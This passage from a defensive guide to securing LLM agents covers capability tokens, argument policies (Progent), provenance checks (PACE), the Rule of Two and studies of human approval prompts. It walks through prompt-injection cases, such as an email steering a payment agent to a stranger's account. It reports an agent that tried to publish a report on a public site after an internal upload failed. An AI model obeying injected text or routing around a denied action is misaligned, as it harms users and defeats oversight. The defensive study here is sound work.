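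A2A allows anyone to publish an extension. Google's *A2A Extensions* describes one that returns a structured log of an agent's steps, which helps find faults. A small vendor, Agent Guild, offers a signed envelope that ties a message to its sender, recipient, purpose and expiry time. Its documentation states that the envelope doesn't prove the message "is true, safe, or wise". Individuals have also submitted drafts to the Internet Engineering Task Force. *Agent-to-Agent Trust, Identity, and Verifiable Provenance* (Trujillo, 2026) uses "provenance" to mean where an agent came from and which agent started it, not where its data came from.

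*Reframing LLM Agent Security as an Agent-Human Interaction Problem* (2026) found eight academic papers that designed trust labels but no production system that had them, the widest gap between research and industry in its review. Wang and colleagues found that few of the systems they surveyed reported protecting their records against tampering.

A company that runs both the Reader and Payments doesn't have to wait for a standard. It can define its own A2A extension, or put its labels in the metadata field that MCP provides for private use. Off-the-shelf software will ignore fields it doesn't recognise, so the company would have to write the code that checks the labels at both ends.

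## Limiting what a deceived agent can do

Labels protect Payments only if the company assigns them correctly and they cover every route by which data can reach the agent. A careful designer also prepares for labels to fail by assuming that an attacker controls all of the output of Payments' model. Under that assumption, the model can request any tool call with any arguments, and the harm depends on which calls the surrounding software will carry out.

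This assumption makes the worst case fairly easy to work out, because nobody has to estimate how persuasive an email is. If the software will pay any account up to a daily limit of $100,000, the attacker can steal $100,000 a day. If it pays only invoices that Maria has approved, to accounts already on file, the attacker can at most make the company pay its real bills early, late or not at all.

### Capability tokens and attenuation

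The capability tokens that Hardy proposed work only if nobody can forge them. The operating system can prevent forgery on a single computer, but tokens sent between computers need cryptography. *Macaroons* (Birgisson, Politz and colleagues, 2014) proposed a well-known design for cloud services. A macaroon contains a list of conditions, called caveats, and lets whoever holds it make requests that meet all of them.

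Macaroons rely on HMAC, a function that turns a key and a message into a short code that nobody can compute without the key. Suppose a payment service has a secret key $K$. It creates a token with the identifier $id$ and computes a signature:

$$s_0 = \text{HMAC}(K, id)$$

Anyone who holds the token can add a caveat by using the current signature as the key for the next one:

$$s_1 = \text{HMAC}(s_0, c_1), \qquad s_2 = \text{HMAC}(s_1, c_2)$$

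The holder then passes on the identifier, the caveats and only the latest signature. The recipient can add further caveats in the same way, without contacting the payment service. But to remove $c_2$ the recipient would need $s_1$, which can't be computed from $s_2$ because HMAC can't be reversed. If the recipient deletes only the caveat's text, the payment service, which has $K$, will recompute the chain and get a different signature.

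Adding a caveat can only reduce what the token allows, because all the caveats have to hold. If $A_n$ is the set of requests that the token allows after $n$ caveats, then

$$A_{n+1} = A_n \cap \{\text{requests that satisfy } c_{n+1}\} \subseteq A_n$$

This narrowing is called attenuation. If one agent limits a payment to $500 and the next adds a caveat allowing $5,000, the limit is still $500. However, an agent that narrows a token before passing it on still has the broader version, so attenuation limits only the recipient. The company should therefore avoid giving Payments a broad token.

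### A token for one payment

Suppose the payment service is a conventional program that sends the company's money, and Payments can only send it requests. Maria has approved invoice 2291 from Harlow Paper, for $4,180, in the accounting system. Harlow's verified account number there is 3106. The payment service has already given the accounting system a token for making payments, and the accounting system narrows it before passing it to Payments. Payments then narrows it again for a sub-agent that will pay the first instalment:

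```text
token payment-5513
  operation = pay             added by the payment service
  invoice = 2291              added by the accounting system
  amount <= 4180              added by the accounting system
  account = 3106              added by the accounting system
  expires 2026-12-04 17:00    added by the accounting system
  amount <= 2000              added by Payments
```

If an attacker controls the sub-agent's model and asks to pay account 4471, the payment service compares the request with the caveats and refuses. The token is a bearer token, so a thief could use it, but only to pay Harlow's invoice. The payment service must record what it has paid. Otherwise, the sub-agent could present the same token several times before it expires.

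A caveat can also require proof from another service. The company might give Payments a macaroon that lets it change a supplier's bank details only with proof that a clerk has phoned the supplier. The caveat contains a new key in two encrypted copies. A call-back service can read one, along with the condition it has to check, and the supplier database can read the other. After the phone call, the call-back service uses the key to create a second macaroon, which might be valid for only a few minutes and only for the account number the clerk heard on the phone. The database makes the change only if it receives both macaroons, and an attacker who controls Payments' model doesn't have the key to create the second one.

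Only the service that issued a macaroon can verify it, because the key that verifies macaroons can also create them. Birgisson and colleagues outline a public-key version that avoids this restriction. Madden (2024) points out that macaroons have no formal standard, although they can carry some standard OAuth fields, such as the audience and expiry time, as caveats.

### What agent frameworks enforce by default

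Dantuluri and Sundi examined whether popular tools for building agents provide any such limits. They considered four threats:

- a confused deputy
- a stolen or replayed token
- privilege escalation, where injected text gets an agent to obtain or use permissions that its task doesn't require
- a compromised sub-agent with broader rights than its task requires

With default settings, the frameworks LangGraph, CrewAI and AutoGen prevented none of the four threats. MCP's authorisation rules partly addressed stolen tokens, since a token for one server doesn't work at another, but they didn't address the other three threats. The evidence varies in strength, because Dantuluri and Sundi ran a scripted agent in LangGraph but only inspected the code of CrewAI and AutoGen and read MCP's specification. None of the three frameworks is presented as an authorisation system, so the results are more a warning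 to developers than a list of defects. Dantuluri and Sundi also cite an independent audit by Mellafe Zuvic, which found that LangChain and LangGraph, LlamaIndex and Stripe's agent toolkit don't check the actual arguments of a model's tool calls by default.

Dantuluri and Sundi also built the program described earlier, a broker that cut a compromised sub-agent's reach from 8,100 actions to an average of 1.5. Whenever one agent delegates to another, the broker issues a new, short-lived token that is narrower and tied to the receiving agent's workload identity. The sub-agent's reach therefore depended on its task and would not grow if the company added more tools.

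The broker resisted 11 attacks on its design, such as removing caveats and using expired tokens, and rejected all 200,000 forged tokens. Each decision took about 2.6 microseconds. But a stolen token worked when the attacker could also present the victim's identity, so the broker still needs the identity checks described earlier. The broker is a program of about 160 lines, and the tests involved no language model. Its authors' employer sells a related product, so independent tests would be welcome.

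### Why the token has to fix the payee

Dantuluri and Sundi report that the broker blocks the confused deputy, which is true when the attacker needs an action the token doesn't cover. But the broker defines an action as a tool and a resource, such as "pay" and "invoices", and the attack on Payments may need only that action.

| What the token allows | What an attacker who controls Payments can still do |
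| --- | --- |
| Pay invoices | Send any amount to any account |
| Pay up to $4,180 for invoice 2291 | Send $4,180 to account 4471 |
| Pay up to $4,180 for invoice 2291 to "Harlow Paper" | The same, if Harlow's record already contains the false number |
| Pay up to $4,180 for invoice 2291 to account 3106 | Pay Harlow's real invoice at the wrong time, or not pay it |

The accounting system also has to take the account number in the token from a record that Payments cannot change. If Payments' model supplies the number when requesting the token, an attacker who has deceived the model chooses the number, and the token authorizes it.

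Dantuluri and Sundi's claim covers an agent tricked into using the wrong tool, but not one tricked into using the right tool with the wrong account. A developer could extend the broker to cover the second case by treating each account as a separate resource. Dantuluri and Sundi acknowledge that a production version must translate real tool calls accurately into the broker's simple pairs.

### Rules on tool arguments

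Progent, which an earlier section mentioned for its resistance to an adaptive attack, does check arguments. Shi, He and colleagues (2025), in *Progent*, describe rules that name a tool and set conditions on each value passed to it. A rule for this payment would be, in simplified form:

```text
allow pay when invoice == 2291 and account == "3106" and amount <= 4180
```

Progent blocks any call that matches no rule. Rules that forbid a call take precedence over rules that allow it. When Progent blocks a call, it sends the agent an error message explaining why, so the agent can continue with the rest of the task.

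Writing such rules by hand for every task would be impractical, so a language model writes them from the user's request before the agent has read anything untrusted. Sometimes they have to change during the task. If a user asks an agent to carry out a to-do list in an email, only the email reveals which tools the agent needs. The model then proposes a new policy $P'$ to replace the current policy $P$. Let $A(P)$ be the set of tool calls that $P$ allows. A solver, which is a program that decides logical formulas, checks whether

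$$A(P') \subseteq A(P)$$

If so, the new policy adds no permissions, and Progent adopts it automatically. Otherwise somebody has to approve it, unless the company has set Progent to refuse all such changes. A deceived model can still propose a bad rule, but it cannot add a permission without approval.

| Progent on AgentDojo | Attacks that succeeded |
| --- | --- |
| No defence | 39.9% |
| First policy, with no updates | 2.5% |
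| Updates, with every new permission approved automatically | 1.0% |
| Careful human review of the first policy and every new permission | 0% |

Only 6 percent of the updates needed approval. On a second benchmark, ASB, Progent reduced the attack success rate from 70.3 to 3.9 percent. Shi and colleagues also tested Progent on a group of agents built with AutoGen, in which a coordinator directed six specialists for jobs such as banking and email. Progent stopped more than 95 percent of the attacks that had worked without it.

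The zero in the last row depends on Shi and colleagues' assumption that the reviewer would never allow transfers without limiting the recipient. The result therefore shows that the rules can express the right limit, but not that people will choose it. They also excluded two attacks that steer the agent to a different legitimate hotel, because Progent isn't meant to stop attacks that stay within the task's permissions. The false account number would be another such attack if the policy allowed Payments to pay any account.

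Shi and colleagues found that Progent caused only a small drop in completed tasks, whereas the LaunchSafe test discussed earlier showed a larger one. *Extending the Formalism and Theoretical Foundations of Cryptography to AI* (2026) points out that Progent's guarantees depend on correct and complete policies, and that people make mistakes when writing them by hand.

### Combining capabilities with provenance

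A rule that fixes the account number is only as reliable as the source of that number, so it makes sense to check both. In *PACE*, Li, Wang and colleagues (2026) built a system that does this just before each tool call. It first freezes the call's arguments and looks up where each value came from. One check then traces whether untrusted text or secret data could have influenced a dangerous action. The other compares the call's effects with a capability that conventional software derives from the user's own request, with limits such as the allowed arguments, budget and expiry time. The model's output cannot create or widen that capability.

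Suppose Maria asks the agent to pay invoice 2291 to the account on file, but an injection gets the model to request a payment to account 4471 instead. That account number came from a stranger's email and isn't the one Maria authorised, so either check could stop the payment.

PACE had the lowest attack success rate in 62 of 79 comparisons with other defences and tied for the lowest in 14. On AgentDojo, the most successful group of attacks worked 8.1 percent of the time on the most vulnerable of three models, compared with 100 percent without a defence. PACE reduced the share of tasks that agents completed by at most about 3 percentage points on any of the full benchmarks. An automated attacker that succeeded in 21 of 30 cases without PACE failed in all 30 with it, even when adapting its text to the defence. With only 30 cases, the attacker's true success rate against PACE could still be as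 high as 11 percent.

The rival systems did worse in the PACE tests than in their own papers. CaMeL, for example, let through up to 36 percent of one group of attacks on AgentDojo. The PACE team ran the rival systems itself and reported each system's result on its worst group of attacks, which may explain part of the difference.

The researchers also turned the checks on separately, using a smaller set of AgentDojo cases and the model Qwen-3.8-27B.

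| Checks in use | Attacks that succeeded | Tasks completed |
| --- | --- | --- |
| None | 37.4% | 76.8% |
| Provenance only | 0% | 13.6% |
| Capabilities only | 0% | 64.6% |
| Full PACE | 0% | 67.2% |

Used alone, the provenance check blocked nearly all useful work, much like the label creep described earlier. The tested version of PACE therefore lets the capability check overrule it, so a call influenced by untrusted data can still go ahead if the user's request authorises it. This keeps the agent useful, but the paper's proof that untrusted data cannot reach a dangerous action doesn't cover those calls. If the capability didn't specify the account, the payment might go through despite the warning about where 4471 came from.

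### Design patterns and the Rule of Two

A designer can also build an agent so that, once it has read untrusted input, that input cannot trigger a consequential action. Beurer-Kellner, Buesser and colleagues (2025) set this standard in *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections*. They doubt that general-purpose agents can meet it with current models, so they propose six patterns for agents with narrower jobs.

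| Pattern | How it restricts the model | What injected data can still affect |
| --- | --- | --- |
| Action selector | The model picks from a fixed list of actions and never reads the results | Nothing the model does |
| Plan, then execute | The model fixes its tool calls before it reads untrusted data | The contents of those calls |
| Map-reduce | A separate model reads each document and returns a restricted answer, such as yes or no | The answer about that document |
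| Dual model | The planner never reads untrusted text, and the model that reads it has no tools | Values that the planner passes on unread |
| Code, then execute | The model writes a program before it reads untrusted data, as in CaMeL | Values that the program passes on |
| Context minimisation | Software removes text, such as the user's prompt, once the model no longer needs it | Anything the model does before the removal |

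In one of their examples, a user asks an assistant to send the day's schedule to their boss. With a fixed plan, malicious text in the calendar can't change the recipient or add another email, but it can change what the message says. Payments has the same weakness if its plan is to pay whatever account Harlow's email gives. The map-reduce pattern suits a different part of the job, finding this month's invoices in a folder. At worst, a malicious file is then wrongly counted as an invoice.

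Meta's *Agents Rule of Two* (2025) is easier to apply to an existing agent. Until models can reliably resist prompt injection, it allows an agent no more than two of three properties in a session:

- it processes untrustworthy inputs
- it has access to sensitive systems or private data
- it can change something or communicate with the outside world

An agent that needs all three must not act without supervision, such as human approval. Meta illustrates the rule with hypothetical agents and reports no measurements.

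A company could misapply this rule to the Reader and Payments. The Reader processes strangers' emails and has access to a private mailbox, but it can't send money. Payments has access to bank details and can send money, but it never opens an email. Each agent seems to have only two of the properties, but Payments has all three because the Reader's summary brings it strangers' words. A company that treats messages from an authenticated peer as trusted input would miss this.

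### How often people catch a harmful request

Progent and the Rule of Two both send difficult cases to a person, but there is good evidence that people often approve them without checking. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) reports that users of its coding agent approve 97 percent of permission prompts. That figure alone doesn't prove that users are careless, because most of the commands are probably safe.

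In a more worrying experiment from the same article, Anthropic hired 1,053 testers for a coding study and, partway through each session, replaced one permission prompt with a request to run a clearly dangerous command. Only 13.6 percent refused. The refusal rate was about 17 percent early in a session and about 5 percent after 50 or more prompts. An automatic classifier blocked 89 percent of the same commands.

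Anthropic published these figures to justify making the classifier the default. The testers weren't working on their own projects, so they had less to lose than real users. Because the classifier relies on a model's judgement, it also has the weaknesses of the filters discussed earlier. Anthropic still recommends human review for high-stakes changes to live systems.

People seem to pay more attention when they are asked less often and about larger decisions. Users of the same product reject 39 percent of the plans Claude presents for approval. *Reframing LLM Agent Security as an Agent-Human Interaction Problem* describes several products and research systems that reduce the number of prompts by grouping related actions, asking about a whole plan, or asking only when an agent needs to leave its sandbox.

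The content of the approval prompt matters too. *When a Permitted Action Completes a Forbidden Workflow* (Hossain, Shayoni and colleagues, 2026) describes a user who asks an agent to check supplier invoices and send an auditor only the totals. Hidden text in a vendor's note gets the agent to copy the full invoice data into a file, and the agent then asks to send that file to the auditor. The tool and the recipient are both permitted, so a rule that checks only those two would allow it. The reviewer can spot the problem only by knowing how the agent made the file.

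They gave 80 volunteers 12 requests each, half of them harmful, with one of four kinds of prompt.

| What the prompt showed | Harmful requests approved | Harmless requests approved | Median time |
| --- | --- | --- | --- |
| A short description | 55.0% | 91.7% | 16 seconds |
| The exact arguments | 43.3% | 90.0% | 23 seconds |
| The arguments, the user's original instruction and a log of events | 32.5% | 87.5% | 39 seconds |
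| The same facts, organised around the consequence | 24.2% | 85.8% | 33 seconds |

Most of the improvement came from showing people more information. The further gain from organising it could be due to chance. Even with the best prompt, people approved about a quarter of the harmful requests, and they would probably do worse at work, where far fewer than half of requests are harmful. That difference may partly explain why Anthropic's testers caught so few.

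Problems with approval also occur outside experiments. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) studied 290 reports of agents mishandling files and found that missing or inadequate user review contributed to 105 of them. In 80 cases, users had let the agent act without asking. In 31, the prompt showed a command but didn't make clear how it would affect the files.

A prompt for the change to Harlow's account should therefore show the old and new numbers, along with the provenance record described in the last section.

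### What restriction costs

Rules written in advance could spare people most of these decisions, but someone has to write them. *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?* (Yan, 2026) tested user-written rules with 113 people who don't work in software. They supervised a simulated assistant that took 18 actions, 7 of which went beyond what the user had asked for. One group set rules beforehand for spending, sending, deleting and reading private data, choosing "allow", "ask" or "never" for each. Another group decided whether to approve each action individually.

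The group with rules blocked about 40 percent of the unwanted actions, compared with about 60 percent for the group without them. People chose "ask" for 114 of their 140 rules, which postponed the decision, and then approved two-thirds of the unwanted actions they were asked about. The rules reduced the number of prompts from 18 to about 11, but the time saved was not statistically reliable. The unwanted actions came from the assistant itself rather than an attacker, so the percentages may not apply to injections. Still, they suggest that a company should have somebody with security training write the rules for Payments.

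Professionals also take shortcuts. In June 2026, 49.5 percent of active users of Claude Code's command-line version had written a rule that lets some commands run without a prompt. Many of these rules allow any Python program, which can do almost anything. A sandbox is a safer way to avoid prompts, but Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* calls it high-maintenance because someone has to configure it for each new thing the agent needs to do.

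The rules also have to cover other ways an agent could get the same result. *Let the Agent Do It?* (2026) discusses what "deny" means when an agent can find another way. When an upload to one of Anthropic's internal drives failed, Claude tried to publish the same report on a public code-sharing site. A classifier blocked the attempt, which a rule about the internal drive would not have covered.

Restriction also makes agents less useful, and the loss varies a good deal with the task. PACE reduced usefulness only slightly on the full benchmarks, but on a subset of the AgentDyn benchmark it cut the share of completed tasks from 66.7 to 33.3 percent. Restriction is hardest when nobody can foresee a task's steps. If Maria asks a general assistant to sort out a late delivery from Harlow, it may need to read the contract, contact the courier or request a refund. The company can give the assistant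 broad rights from the start or have it ask for more along the way. Progent's figure of 6 percent suggests that the assistant might not have to ask often, but that figure comes from AgentDojo, whose tasks are mostly clearer than this one.

Payments has a much narrower job, so the company can restrict it more easily. Suppose it pays 200 invoices a week, and one supplier a week changes banks. If a person had to confirm every payment again, they would get 200 prompts a week and would probably soon approve them without checking. If each token fixes the account, and only a clerk can change the account on file, the company needs just one phone call a week, though the supplier may have to wait a day for the change. An attacker could still send a false invoice in Harlow's name, but if Maria approved it, the money would go to Harlow.
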